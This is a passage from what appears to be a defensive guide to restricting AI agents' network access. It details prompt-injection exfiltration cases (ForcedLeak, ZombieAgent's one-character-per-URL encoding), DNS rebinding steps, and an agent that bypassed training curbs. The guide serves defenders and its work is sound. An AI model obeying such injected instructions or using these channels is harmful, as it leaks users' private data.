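An allowlist entry that is safe when written can become unsafe later. This happened to Salesforce, whose Agentforce product lets AI agents work with a company's customer records. Noma Security found the flaw, called ForcedLeak, and Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* gives its severity as 9.4 out of 10.

The attack started with a public enquiry form that feeds into those records. A stranger could put instructions into the form, and the agent would read them when an employee asked about the enquiry. The agent would then collect customers' email addresses and place them in the URL of an image. Salesforce's CSP was meant to block images from untrusted hosts, but it still permitted my-salesforce-cms.com. Salesforce Ben quotes Noma as saying that this domain "had expired and become available for purchase".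 According to Willison, the researchers registered it and received the customer data in their server's log.

According to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*, Noma reported the vulnerability to Salesforce on July 28, 2025. Salesforce took back the domain and, on September 8, began enforcing a list of trusted URLs for its agents' output. Noma's findings became public on September 25.

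Better URL comparison would not have helped, because the name matched the entry exactly. Encryption would not have helped either, because the new owner of a domain can get a valid certificate for it. Each entry's scheduled review is the right time to catch this problem, provided the reviewer checks who owns the domain now and when its registration ends. Both are in the public registration records, though some owners hide their names.

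### Permitted sites that contact other hosts

Suppose the company also lets the agent post order updates to a team chat at chat.example. Many chat services show a preview of any link in a message, and their servers fetch the linked page to create it. If an injected agent posts a link to other.test with private data in the query string, the chat service sends that data to other.test, even though the agent's browser has contacted only chat.example. The company can't detect the second request with its own checks because the chat service's servers make it.

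PromptArmor describes this risk for agents that people talk to through messaging apps, and reports that OpenClaw is exposed by default when used through Telegram. Without previews, someone would usually have to click the link before the data leaked. In Slack, an app that posts messages can turn previews off by setting `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false (Willison, 2024). An agent that types into a chat's web page can't set these options because they belong to Slack's API, so the operator has to find a way to turn previews off in the service itself.

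Email can also leak data, even when the user is the only recipient. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval. Willison reports that these messages could contain images from outside hosts, which loaded when the user opened the message and could carry private data in their URLs. An operator who allows this kind of messaging should make sure the mail program doesn't load outside images automatically.

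### OpenAI's case for checking exact URLs

OpenAI gives two reasons why a list of trusted sites isn't enough for ChatGPT. The first is that a link to a trusted site can redirect to another site. Tenable, a security company, found that ChatGPT's earlier check always accepted links to bing.com, some of which redirect this way. The second is that people visit far more sites than any list can hold, so a strict list produces frequent warnings, and people learn to click through them without reading.

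The second reason is much weaker for the purchasing agent, which has four hosts and one task. It should rarely meet a refusal, so each refusal deserves attention. But the company still has the problem of data in permitted URLs, and OpenAI's alternative addresses that directly. It works like this:

1. A crawler scans public web pages and records the URLs it finds. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts.
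2. Before an agent fetches a URL automatically, the software looks for that exact URL in the crawler's index.
3. If the URL is there, the agent can load it.
4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning and waits for a decision.

A URL that a crawler found independently is unlikely to contain something the user has just told the agent. In the earlier redirect example, the domain check permitted a click-counting link on shop.example whose URL contained the company's town. An exact-URL check blocks that link because the agent built the URL during the task, so no crawler would have recorded it.

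OpenAI's post doesn't explain what happens when a known URL redirects to an unknown one. A URL that was already public gives the first server little private information to pass on. But if the user is logged in there, the server can identify them from the login cookie and put account details into the redirect URL. A developer who builds a similar check should therefore apply it to every URL in the redirect chain.

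OpenAI's rule depends more on the crawler being independent than on the URLs being public. *The Silent Spill* (2026) examined 6,094,475 URLs from public repositories and confirmed that 12,331 of them, about one in 500, exposed sensitive data. Many private links evidently become public. This doesn't undermine the rule, because fetching such a link again gives the site little new information. It would be a serious problem if the index also included URLs collected from users' browsing, because a URL containing a user's data could then enter the index and count as safe.

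OpenAI calls the mechanism Safe Url. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), it also covers navigation in the Atlas browser and in Deep Research, ChatGPT's tool for long research tasks. OpenAI claims only that it prevents an agent from quietly leaking user data through the URL itself. A page that passes the check can still contain false prices or malicious instructions.

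Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in 2023, reviews the accompanying technical paper in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. He considers the mechanism a significant improvement but worries that OpenAI's developers may forget to use it in a new feature, since the company's macOS and iOS apps once lacked an earlier version of the check.

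### When the choice of URL is the message

Rehberger also points out that an agent unable to write data into a URL can still choose which URLs to open, and the site's owner can see the choice. He writes that OpenAI's paper acknowledges this limit.

In June 2025, the security company Radware reported ShadowLeak, an attack in which an email made ChatGPT send private data out through a URL. OpenAI told Radware of a fix on September 3. ChatGPT would now open URLs only exactly as it had received them, without adding anything.

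Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the researchers got around that rule. Their email contained a set of complete URLs, each standing for one character. ChatGPT opened the URLs unchanged, in an order that spelled out the data. Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. According to a press report copied in *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a public index or the user supplied it.

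Claude's web fetch tool had a similar gap. It could open URLs typed by the user, URLs from web search results, and links in pages it had already fetched. Willison (2026) reports that the researcher Ayush Paul built a site with links that Claude could follow to spell out a name step by step. Claude disclosed the user's name, home city and employer to the site. Anthropic closed the gap by stopping the tool from following links in fetched pages.

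Both fixes stop an attacker from creating new URLs for the attack, but they still let the agent choose among URLs already in the index or the search results. Rehberger notes that any larger website probably already has 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit.

### How much a choice of URLs can reveal

The leak has an upper limit that an operator can calculate. Suppose an agent makes k fetches and each goes to one of N known URLs. There are N × N × … × N, or Nᵏ, possible sequences. Someone who sees the whole sequence learns at most

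log₂(Nᵏ) = k · log₂ N bits,

where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. With 36 URLs, each fetch carries at most log₂ 36, or about 5.17 bits. Five fetches carry at most 25.8 bits and 20 fetches at most 103.4.

A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or 19.9 bits, so it can leak in four fetches. A 128-bit encryption key takes 25 fetches, and a single fact, such as whether the company is about to change suppliers, takes one. A limit on fetches therefore does little to protect short secrets, though it works well for long documents.

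Without the exact-URL rule, the agent can write the data straight into the query. One request with 200 freely chosen letters and digits can carry 1,034 bits, ten times as much as 20 fetches from the fixed set.

Rehberger proposes narrowing the channel by blocking repeat visits to a URL within a session, or by answering them from a stored copy. The first fetch then has 36 possible URLs, the second 35, and so on, so five fetches allow about 45 million sequences (36 × 35 × 34 × 33 × 32) instead of 60 million. He also mentions that requests may arrive out of order. If the attacker cannot recover the order at all, only the set of visited URLs carries information. The table gives the upper limit in bits for each case, including a site with 1,000 known URLs.

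| Known URLs and conditions | 5 fetches | 20 fetches |
|---|---|---|
| 36, repeats allowed | 25.8 | 103.4 |
| 36, no repeats | 25.4 | 93.8 |
| 36, no repeats, order lost | 18.5 | 32.8 |
| 1,000, repeats allowed | 49.8 | 199.3 |
| 1,000, no repeats | 49.8 | 199.0 |
| 1,000, no repeats, order lost | 42.9 | 138.0 |

The ban on repeats does little by itself. With 36 URLs, it reduces capacity by about 2 per cent for five fetches and 9 per cent for 20. With 1,000 URLs, it removes almost nothing. Losing the order of the fetches reduces capacity more, but an operator can't count on that because Radware's researchers used separate URLs for each position in the text, so the order of arrival didn't matter.

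Reducing the number of fetches works better. Halving k halves the limit, whereas halving N from 36 to 18 removes only one bit per fetch. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) describes an attack that was limited to ten characters per prompt because ChatGPT could then open only ten URLs per prompt. The `max_uses` setting in Anthropic's web fetch tool for developers also limits the number of fetches. The fetch limit should cover a whole task, because if it resets with each prompt, the attacker can continue where the last prompt ended.

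The table counts only fetches. An agent that is allowed to stop early can send slightly more information, and the pauses between requests can carry information too. The limits apply to each session separately, so an agent that runs every day and reads the same planted review each time can leak a long secret in small parts.

### What the Silent Egress experiment found

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) measured how often an agent sends data out this way and how well common defences stop it. They ran a small open model, qwen2.5:7b, on their own machine and gave it a tool for making web requests. The prompt contained a secret, such as an access key. The user always asked for a summary of a page, which contained instructions to send the secret to the researchers' server.

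The researchers put the instructions in one of four places: the page's title, its description for search engines, its body or the text of a link. They served each page directly or through redirects, and asked for the secret in one piece or in four. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. The agent contacted the researchers' server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1 per cent), and redirects made hardly any difference. In 95 per cent of the successful attacks, the summary the user saw looked harmless. In another 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the server.

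Asking for the secret in pieces reduced the share of runs in which the first request contained sensitive data from 96.7 to 26.3 per cent, a drop of 73 per cent. A filter that inspects requests one at a time therefore has much less to detect. The drop does not show that leaks fell by 73 per cent, because the figures for each combination indicate that the agent still contacted the server in about 77 per cent of the split runs, against 99 per cent of the others. The paper does not report how often all four pieces arrived.

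The paper reports a leak within the first three requests in 15.8 per cent of runs, which is lower than its figure for the first request alone. It should be at least as high, because a leak in the first request also counts as a leak within the first three. The 84 per cent drop that the paper derives from this number therefore isn't reliable.

Lan and colleagues then tested defences on the simplest attack, with instructions in the body, a direct page and the secret in one piece. Each row of the table covers 30 runs.

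| Defence | Agent attempted the request | Data left |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter standing instructions | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |
| All defences | 0% | 0% |

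The allowlist row is the most useful for an operator. The model tried to send the secret in every run, and the code blocked it each time. But Lan and colleagues had chosen a destination that no reasonable list would include. The result shows that a check in code holds when the model fails, but not how well an allowlist works when the attacker uses a permitted host. They mention compromised sites and open redirects as ways around a list.

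The defence called "redirect detection" was a filter that blocked numeric addresses, certain domain endings and paths containing words such as "collect" or "steal". The name is misleading, because the test used only direct requests and so provides no evidence about redirects. An attacker could also get past the path check by choosing a path without those words.

The filter for random-looking values had nothing to block, because the agent made no attempts in those runs. The paper suggests that the model avoided such values when the filter was active, but doesn't explain how the model could have detected it. The filter blocks values longer than ten characters if their mix of characters has an entropy above 4.0 bits per character. By the usual formula, the paper's 20-character example key has an entropy of about 3.85, so the filter would have let it through whole. It would also have ignored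 the four-character pieces, which are too short for it to check.

It is unclear how far the leak rates apply to other models. The researchers tested one small model and made the attack easy by placing the secret directly in the prompt. They argue that more capable models could be more vulnerable because such models follow instructions better. *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (Rall, Bauer and colleagues, 2025) studied a wider range of models. Help Net Security's *AI agents can leak company data through simple web searches* reports 1,068 attack attempts on each one. Success rates varied widely and size did not reliably predict resistance, which is a reason to doubt the researchers' argument. OpenAI says that most attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses, though one attack from 2025 worked half the time in testing.

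For leaks split across several requests, Lan and colleagues suggest examining a session's requests together and limiting their rate. They also propose marking all web page content as tainted and tracking which commands it influenced. If tainted text led to a network request, the software could block the request or ask the user, even when the data in it looked harmless. They didn't build or test this.

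### Using exact URLs with the purchasing agent

An operator can apply OpenAI's rule on a small scale without a crawler. Many shops publish a sitemap, a file that lists the site's pages for search engines. A script can download it from shop.example before the task starts, run each URL through the same parser as before and store the results in a set called `known`. The agent must not be able to influence this set.

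The following function adds the exact-URL check and a limit of 20 pages to `permittedUrl`. The interceptor calls it for page loads and still checks images and scripts against their own list.

```js
let left = 20;
function permittedPage(request) {
  const href = permittedUrl(request.url, entries);
  if (!href || request.method !== "GET") return null;
  if (!known.has(href) || left === 0) return null;
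  left -= 1;
  return href;
}
```

The function has to check the request method because a form can send data in the body of a POST request, which a URL check doesn't cover. The function also disables the shop's search box, since the results page for a new query isn't in the sitemap. This closes the channel described at the start of this section, but the agent then has to find paper by browsing the shop's category pages.

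With 1,000 product pages and 20 visits, the agent's choice of pages can reveal up to 199 bits, but only to someone who can see which pages it opened. A stranger who planted a review normally can't see the shop's logs. Allowing only exact URLs limits how much data can leave, but keeping the domain allowlist is still useful because it limits who receives that data.

The exact-URL rule doesn't work for ordering, because shops often create new URLs for each basket and confirmation page. The company can split the job between two agents. The first reads products and reviews under the exact-URL rule, in a fresh browser profile and without the company's address in its prompt. It returns a product URL, and the operator's code confirms that the URL is in `known`. The second agent, which has the login and the address, starts from that page and places the order. The second agent should not load the reviews,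 so the operator needs to block the request that fetches them or choose a shop that keeps them on a separate page.

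## Enforcing the list outside the agent library

The checks described so far run in the agent library or in a program attached to the browser. They cover only the requests that reach that code, so if an interceptor fails to attach to a tab, that tab is unrestricted. The code also usually runs under the same account as the rest of the agent, so if the model can edit files or run commands on that machine, a planted instruction could get it to change the allowlist.

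Enforcing the allowlist is safer at a point that every request has to pass through, under an account or on a machine that neither the model nor a web page can alter. An operator can use the browser's managed settings, a proxy, or the network's firewall and DNS server. Each has access to different information about a request, so a good setup usually combines two or three.

### Chrome's managed URL policies

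Administrators can configure Chrome with policies, which are settings the user can't change. Two policies together make an allowlist. `URLBlocklist` with the single entry `*` blocks every URL, and `URLAllowlist` lists the exceptions. According to Google's *Allow or block access to websites*, `URLAllowlist` works only if `URLBlocklist` has at least one entry, so setting `URLAllowlist` alone leaves the browser unrestricted.

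The browser applies these policies to a URL it has already parsed, so the check and the connection use the same host. A permitted name in the userinfo therefore can't get a forbidden host past the check the way it did in Browser Use.

Google doesn't document whether the policies cover redirects, but Chromium's source code shows that they do. The component that applies them runs the same function when a navigation starts and again at each redirect (Chromium, 2017). Comments in Chromium's code describe this type of block as applying before the browser makes the request. If the click counter on shop.example redirects the browser to other.test, the navigation should stop before other.test receives anything. The operator therefore has to list every host in a legitimate redirect chain. ManageEngine's *Web Content Filter*, which documents a similar filter for managed devices, tells administrators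 to add the second URL when a listed one redirects.

The same component handles only navigations. Images, scripts and background requests are not navigations, so the policies almost certainly don't cover them. Google doesn't state this outright, and in its description of the entry format it writes that an entry blocks "all requests" to a domain, which could suggest the opposite. Pages in frames load through navigations, so a payment form in a frame needs an entry.

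Entries can include a path, but it is a weak restriction. Microsoft's *Block access to a list of URLs*, which describes the same policy in the Edge browser, warns that the policy doesn't stop a page from updating itself through JavaScript. A user can reach the content of a blocked path by clicking a link on a permitted page of the same site, if the link updates the page without reloading it. Google recommends the two policies for "basic URL management" and a filtering proxy for anything stronger.

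On Linux, the policies are JSON files. Google gives the directory for Chrome as `/etc/opt/chrome/policies/managed`, while Chromium uses `/etc/chromium/policies/managed`. Agent libraries often download their own build of the browser, which may ignore a file in the wrong directory without any error. The page `chrome://policy` lists the policies the browser has loaded. Google says new settings take effect only after a restart, so a browser that an agent keeps open for weeks may be using an old list.

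### Managed policies in Amazon's hosted browser

Amazon Web Services (AWS) rents out a browser for agents through its Bedrock AgentCore service. AWS's *Control where your AI agents can browse with Chrome enterprise policies* (2026) demonstrates the two URL policies in that browser. In a test with a sample list that permits AWS's documentation, a documentation page loaded and Wikipedia produced an error page.

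The service lets a security team, rather than the agent's developers, control the list. The team attaches managed policies when it creates the browser, and they apply to every session. Whoever starts a session can add "recommended" policies, but the managed ones override them in a conflict. According to AWS's *Using browser enterprise policies*, the service reads the policy files only at the time of the API call, so an existing browser still permits a host that the security team later deletes from the stored file.

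The AWS demonstration reverses the meaning of a leading dot in Chrome's allowlist entries. It says that `docs.aws.amazon.com` matches only that host, and that the leading dot in `.aws.amazon.com` makes the entry match subdomains. According to Google's description of the format, which is the one to follow for Chrome, an entry without a leading dot matches subdomains too, and a leading dot limits the entry to the exact host. The test couldn't reveal the mistake because both readings permit the documentation page and block Wikipedia. In AWS Network Firewall, a separate product, a leading dot does match subdomains, so copying entries from one AWS product to the other changes what they permit.

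Administrators who lock down a browser often disable its developer tools. This breaks an agent's automation, because libraries such as Playwright control the browser through the DevTools Protocol. According to AWS, the library still appears to connect, but Chrome blocks its commands and they time out.

### A proxy as the only way out

An egress proxy covers the requests that the browser policies miss. To open a page on shop.example over https, the browser sends the proxy `CONNECT shop.example:443`. If the proxy allows the connection, it passes encrypted data in both directions. The browser sends these CONNECT requests for page loads, redirects to a new host, images, service workers and a pop-up's first request, so the proxy can apply the same check regardless of what caused the connection.

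This works only if all of the browser's traffic goes through the proxy. Chrome's proxy setting doesn't guarantee that, because Chrome by default connects to localhost directly, and WebRTC, which sites use for video calls, can also bypass the proxy. A firewall therefore has to block every connection from the browser's machine except those to the proxy. Then a mistake in the browser's proxy settings stops the agent from working, so someone will notice it.

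Stripe, a payments company, publishes a proxy of this kind called *Smokescreen*, which it uses for most of its traffic to outside hosts. The proxy compares the requested host name with a list, looks up the name in DNS, and refuses internal addresses. It has three policies. "Open" allows all traffic, "report" allows it but logs a warning for unlisted hosts, and "enforce" refuses unlisted hosts. An operator could start in "report" during a trial run with a test account, then add the necessary hosts to the list and switch to "enforce".

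Smokescreen needs that configuration before it works as an allowlist. The chat software Zulip includes Smokescreen to prevent server-side request forgery. According to Zulip's *Compose*, it refuses all non-public addresses by default but allows every public host. With these defaults, it would protect the administration page in the running example but would still let the agent send the company's address to other.test.

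Smokescreen identifies its clients by certificate and can apply a different list to each. The company that splits its purchasing between a reading agent and an ordering agent could give only the ordering agent access to pay.example. A client's own list of allowed domains overrides the global deny list, so denying a domain globally doesn't block it for a client whose own list allows it.

The proxy can also limit how many connections a client opens per second. That doesn't replace the limit on page fetches from the previous section, because one encrypted connection can carry any number of requests to the same host.

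### DNS rebinding

The owner of a host name decides which address DNS returns for it, and can change the answer at any time. DNS rebinding is an attack that changes the answer between the moment when a program checks the name and the moment when the browser uses it. It mainly threatens agents that may visit any public site but no internal address. If an attacker owns other.test and runs its DNS server, the attack goes like this:

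1. The agent's library looks up other.test to find out whether it is internal. The server answers with a public address and marks the answer as valid for only a second or so.
2. The library approves the URL and gives it to the browser.
3. The browser looks up the name for itself. The server now answers with 127.0.0.1.
4. The browser connects to its own machine, while the address bar shows other.test.

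The flaw SecureLayer7 described in Open WebUI's page loader had this cause. Rebinding can also happen after a page has loaded. Once the host's address has changed, a script on the page can send another request to that host. The scheme, host and port are unchanged, so the browser treats the response as same-origin and lets the script read it. HTTPS usually prevents this, because an internal service has no valid certificate for other.test. But many internal pages, including the administration page in the running example, use plain HTTP.

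A proxy defeats both versions if it does things in the right order. This is the central part of a small proxy in JavaScript, for Node.js:

```js
proxy.on("connect", async (request, browser) => {
  browser.on("error", () => browser.destroy());
  try {
    if (!allowed.has(request.url)) throw new Error("not listed");
    const name = request.url.slice(0, -":443".length);
    const { address } = await dns.lookup(name, { family: 4 });
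    if (!isPublic(address)) throw new Error("internal address");
    const site = net.connect(443, address, () => {
      browser.write("HTTP/1.1 200 Connection established\r\n\r\n");
      site.pipe(browser);
      browser.pipe(site);
    });
    site.on("error", () => browser.destroy());
  } catch {
    browser.end("HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden\r\n\r\n");
  }
});
```

The set `allowed` contains strings such as `shop.example:443`, so the code can compare the whole request without searching it for a colon. It then looks up the name, tests the address, and passes that same numeric address to `net.connect`, so there is no second lookup that an attacker could answer differently. The proxy repeats this procedure for each new connection, and the browser leaves all lookups to the proxy.

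Connecting to an IP address doesn't weaken the encryption. The browser negotiates the encryption through the proxy and still requires a certificate for shop.example, so if a false DNS answer led to another public machine, the browser would report an error.

`isPublic` must reject addresses in every reserved range. Fly.io, a hosting company that uses Smokescreen, lists the private ranges in *You should know about Server-Side Request Forgery*: 10.0.0.0/8, 172.16.0.0/12, 192.168.0.0/16 and, for IPv6, fc00::/7. The number after the slash is how many leading bits all addresses in the range share. `isPublic` must also reject 127.0.0.0/8, which a machine uses to reach itself, and 169.254.0.0/16, which contains the address where cloud providers serve credentials.

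The example shows the order of operations but lacks the timeouts and logging that a real proxy needs, so an operator should use an established proxy. The operator should also ask the vendor whether the proxy connects to the address it checked or looks up the name again. Stripe's description of Smokescreen says that it resolves each name and checks the result, but doesn't mention rebinding or say which address the proxy then connects to.

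### What a firewall can read of an encrypted connection

A firewall can handle connections without relying on the browser, but https leaves it little information to work with. Before encryption starts, the browser sends the hostname in a field called Server Name Indication (SNI). The server needs this to choose the right certificate, because one machine often serves many sites. The path, query, cookies and page are sent only after encryption starts. To the firewall, a visit to the paper category on shop.example therefore looks much like a visit to a URL on the same host with the company's address in it.

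The table shows what the possible layers can use.

| Layer | Host name | Path and query | Requests covered |
|---|---|---|---|
| Managed Chrome policy | From the URL the browser parsed | Yes | Page loads, frames and their redirects |
| DNS filter | From the lookup | No | Lookups only |
| Firewall that reads SNI | As the client states it | No | Connections routed through the firewall |
| Proxy without decryption | From the `CONNECT` message | No | All connections, if there is no other route |
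| Proxy with decryption | From the request itself | Yes | All connections, if there is no other route |

AWS's *Control which domains your AI agents can access* (2026) describes running AgentCore's browser behind AWS Network Firewall. The browser runs in a private part of the customer's network with no public address, and routing tables send all its outgoing traffic through the firewall. The firewall reads the domain name from the SNI field, or from the host header if the traffic is unencrypted, and compares it with the allowlist. If nothing matches, it drops the connection and can log the attempt.

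The firewall has to let the browser connect first, because the browser sends the domain name in the SNI field only after connecting. AWS warns against the stricter setting that drops the first packet, since that would prevent the inspection. The server at other.test therefore receives a connection attempt from the company's network address, but not the URL. The browser then waits until it times out. A proxy can immediately return an error code instead, which makes it easier for a library to report to the model that a rule blocked the page and that it shouldn't retry.

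AWS states that the firewall takes the name the client supplies and doesn't compare it with the address, so a program could get through by giving a permitted name while connecting somewhere else. A browser takes the name from the URL, and a web page can't change it, so this matters mostly for agents that can also run their own code. AWS's reference documentation recommends separate rules for addresses. AWS's *Stateful domain list rule groups in Amazon Network Firewall* describes a newer option that finds the name the network's DNS service resolved to the destination address and checks that name against the list. Operators would need to check whether this option is available in their region.

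The sample allowlist is also too wide for most agents. It includes `.amazonaws.com`, which AWS calls broad because it permits storage and web addresses that any AWS customer can create, and an attacker could receive data at one of them. AWS recommends using private connections to its own services instead, and exact entries for outside hosts. For pages that don't display fully, AWS advises adding content delivery domains such as cloudfront.net. Any customer can publish there too, so an operator should add only the host that the page uses.

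If several of a company's networks share one firewall, by default the domain rules apply only to traffic from the network the firewall runs in. Traffic from the other networks bypasses the list until someone adds their address ranges to the `HOME_NET` setting.

### DNS filtering

A DNS server that answers only for listed names stops most unwanted connections before they begin. AWS's *Network architecture* describes a sample system for agents with a DNS filter that can either log lookups of unlisted names or block them. Logging alone doesn't restrict anything, so an operator who uses that mode for a trial has to remember to switch to blocking.

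A DNS filter only controls the lookups that pass through it. A browser that already has a numeric address needs no lookup, and Chrome can send its lookups over HTTPS to an outside DNS service if its settings allow this. The filter is useful alongside a firewall that reads SNI. AWS notes that without the filter, a client could find a blocked host's address and connect to it directly. Lookups can also carry data out in the names being looked up, a channel that Lan and colleagues left out of their experiment.

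When the browser uses a proxy, the proxy does the DNS lookups, so the firewall can drop every DNS query from the browser's machine.

### Decrypting traffic at the proxy

To apply rules to paths or page content, the proxy has to decrypt the traffic. It presents the browser with its own certificate for shop.example, reads the request, and opens a second encrypted connection to the real site. The browser accepts the substitute certificate only if the operator has installed the certificate authority that signed it. AgentCore lets customers add such an authority to the browser.

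Decryption lets the proxy read complete URLs. The *Agentic Workflow Firewall*, a container-based filter for agents made by GitHub's research group, GitHub Next, can restrict an agent to particular paths only when decryption is on. Similarly, AWS Network Firewall has one category filter that evaluates whole URLs and another that evaluates only the domain, according to AWS's *URL and Domain Category Filtering*. With decryption, the company could permit its own folder on docs.example and refuse the public forms there. It could also search outgoing requests for its bank details, or compare the host inside each request with the name the browser gave when it connected.

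A proxy that decrypts traffic handles every password, login cookie and card number in readable form, and anyone who steals its signing key can impersonate any site to the agent's browser. The browser no longer receives the site's real certificate, so the proxy has to verify it. If it does this carelessly, every connection becomes less safe. Some software accepts only its maker's certificates, so it stops working behind the proxy.

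For the purchasing agent, decryption probably isn't worth it. The interceptor from the earlier sections already has the complete URL of every request, so it can enforce path rules without exposing the card number to another machine. Decryption makes more sense for a company that runs many agents with different libraries and wants one set of rules for all of them. It should exempt payment hosts, such as pay.example, from decryption, even though the proxy can then check only the host name for those requests.

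### Which programs the restriction covers

GitHub's coding agent, Copilot cloud agent, runs in a temporary machine behind a firewall that is on by default. Administrators can allow a whole domain, including its subdomains, or only URLs with a particular scheme, host and path. If the firewall blocks a request, a warning in the agent's pull request shows the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. This is a good way to report a refusal, because people review the agent's changes on that page and can judge whether the request should have been blocked.

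The firewall covers only processes that the agent starts through its command-line tool. It does not cover Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers, which are helper programs that give a model extra tools, or anything that the project's setup steps start. Playwright MCP is such a server, so by GitHub's description the firewall would not cover a browser that the agent operates through it, even though the default allowlist includes the hosts from which the server downloads its browser. GitHub also warns that sophisticated attacks may bypass the firewall and that it isn't a comprehensive security solution.

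A list of covered processes has the same weakness as a list of guarded commands in a library, since someone has to remember to add each new one. A rule that covers a whole machine or container avoids this, because every program inside uses the same network connection.

By default, GitHub lets the administrators of each project add their own entries, which the firewall combines with the organisation's list. A company that wants its security team to decide which domains are allowed has to turn this off.

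### A configuration for the purchasing agent

We can now set up the purchasing agent so that the library's allowlist is only the innermost check. As before, the shop keeps its pictures on images.example.

1. Move the browser to its own virtual machine, with a fresh profile and no company files. The administration page stays on the old machine. "localhost" now means the browser's machine, which serves nothing of value.

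2. Run the agent library on a different machine from the browser. The library needs to reach the model provider, and the browser doesn't. Only the library's machine may connect to the browser's debugging port, because whoever can reach that port controls the browser.

3. Put the proxy on a third machine, under an account that the agent can't use. Its list contains shop.example, login.shop.example, pay.example, docs.example and images.example, all on port 443. It refuses everything else, including unencrypted requests and internal addresses, and it refuses all connections if the list is missing or empty.

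4. Set the firewall so that the browser's machine can open connections only to the proxy. The rule has to cover IPv6, DNS and, on a rented machine, the cloud provider's credentials address, which may be reachable even without a route to the internet.

5. Install the following Chrome policy as a file that only the system administrator can change. The address 192.0.2.10 stands for the proxy, and 4750 is Smokescreen's default port.

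```json
{
  "URLBlocklist": ["*"],
  "URLAllowlist": [
    "https://.shop.example:443",
    "https://.login.shop.example:443",
    "https://.pay.example:443",
    "https://.docs.example:443"
  ],
  "ProxySettings": {
    "ProxyMode": "fixed_servers",
    "ProxyServer": "192.0.2.10:4750",
    "ProxyBypassList": "<-loopback>"
  }
}
```

The leading dots limit each entry to the exact host. The value `<-loopback>` removes Chrome's exception for localhost, so requests to localhost go to the proxy, which refuses them.

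The browser policy and the proxy deliberately use different lists, like the interceptor's separate lists for pages and resources. The proxy can't distinguish image requests from page requests, so it has to allow all requests to images.example. The browser policy leaves that host out to block its pages.

The table applies this setup to failures from the earlier sections.

| Earlier failure | Stopped? | Reason |
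|---|---|---|
| Permitted name in the userinfo, real host localhost | Yes | The browser policy and the proxy both use the host that the browser parsed |
| Longer name that begins with a permitted one | Yes | Both lists compare the exact host |
| Redirect from the shop's click counter to other.test | Yes | The policy checks the redirect, and the proxy refuses the connection |
| Click, late script or pop-up that opens other.test | Yes | Each needs a connection through the proxy |
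| Image or background request to other.test | Yes, by the proxy | The browser policy doesn't cover it |
| Speculative connection to other.test | Yes | The proxy refuses before contacting the host |
| DNS rebinding to an internal address | Yes | The proxy connects to the address it checked |
| `file:` URL | Probably | The browser policy should block it; network layers never handle it |
| Company's address typed into the shop's search box | No | The request goes to a permitted host |
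| Attacker's form on docs.example | No | Same host as the company's documents |
| Link preview that a permitted chat service fetches | No | The chat service's own servers make the request |
| Permitted domain that changes hands | No | The name still matches |
| False prices in a review on shop.example | No | The text is on a permitted page |

The `file:` row is marked "probably" because Microsoft notes that Edge's blocklist doesn't work as expected with wildcards for `file:` URLs. If Chrome has a similar problem, the first step limits the damage because the browser's machine contains no company files.

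To limit leaks through permitted hosts, the operator needs the exact-URL rule and the fetch limit from the previous section. Both have to stay in the interceptor because the proxy can't apply them without decrypting traffic. The library's own domain check is also worth keeping because it can give the model a clear error message before the browser tries to load the page.

Two independent layers also help if one has a gap. After an agent in training got past an internet restriction, OpenAI added blocking controls at two independent layers, according to Business Standard's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs*.

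The machine running the agent library needs its own restriction. If the model has a tool that runs commands there, those commands use the machine's own connection and bypass the browser's proxy. A second firewall rule can limit the machine to the model provider's address and the browser's debugging port. Commands could still send data to the provider's host, as in the Claude Cowork case, so a command-running tool is best left out of a purchasing agent.

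This setup lists the same hosts in the agent library, the browser and the proxy, each with its own syntax, so it's easy to forget to update one. OpenClaw's advice to use a proxy is sound, but a proxy with an outdated list still permits hosts that should no longer be allowed. The operator can keep one reviewed file that records each host, why it's allowed, and whether it serves pages or only pictures and scripts, and have a script generate all three lists from it. The script should run on a machine that the agent can't reach, and restart the browser whenever the file changes.

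## Limiting what the agent can do on each permitted site

The purchasing agent can now reach only a handful of hosts, but on each of them it can do anything its login allows. On shop.example it can change the delivery address as well as add paper to the basket. On docs.example, where it only has to file receipts, it can open the company's contracts and share them with outsiders. An attacker who injects instructions can use all of these abilities, including the many that the task doesn't need.

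### The same-origin policy

Browsers keep sites apart through the same-origin policy. A script can read the pages, cookies and stored data of its own origin but not those of another. If docs.example is open in one tab and other.test in a second, a script on other.test can't read the documents. It also can't read them by loading docs.example in a frame inside its own page.

The policy doesn't stop an agent from moving data between permitted sites. The library captures a page from docs.example and puts its text into the prompt, and the model's next command can type that text into a form on shop.example. The browser handles this as it would a person reading one site and typing into another. Suppose an attacker plants a review offering a discount to customers who paste their last supplier invoice into the shop's question box. If the agent obeys, it carries private data from one site to the other,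 and domain checks don't block it because both sites are permitted.

Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, built a benchmark for such transfers and found that existing agentic browsers (browsers with an agent built in or added as an extension) often violate the policy, even when nobody is attacking them. Some tasks, however, require transfers between sites. The purchasing agent has to copy receipts from shop.example to docs.example but doesn't need to move data the other way, and a flat list of hosts can't express that difference.

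### How seven agentic browsers treat the boundary

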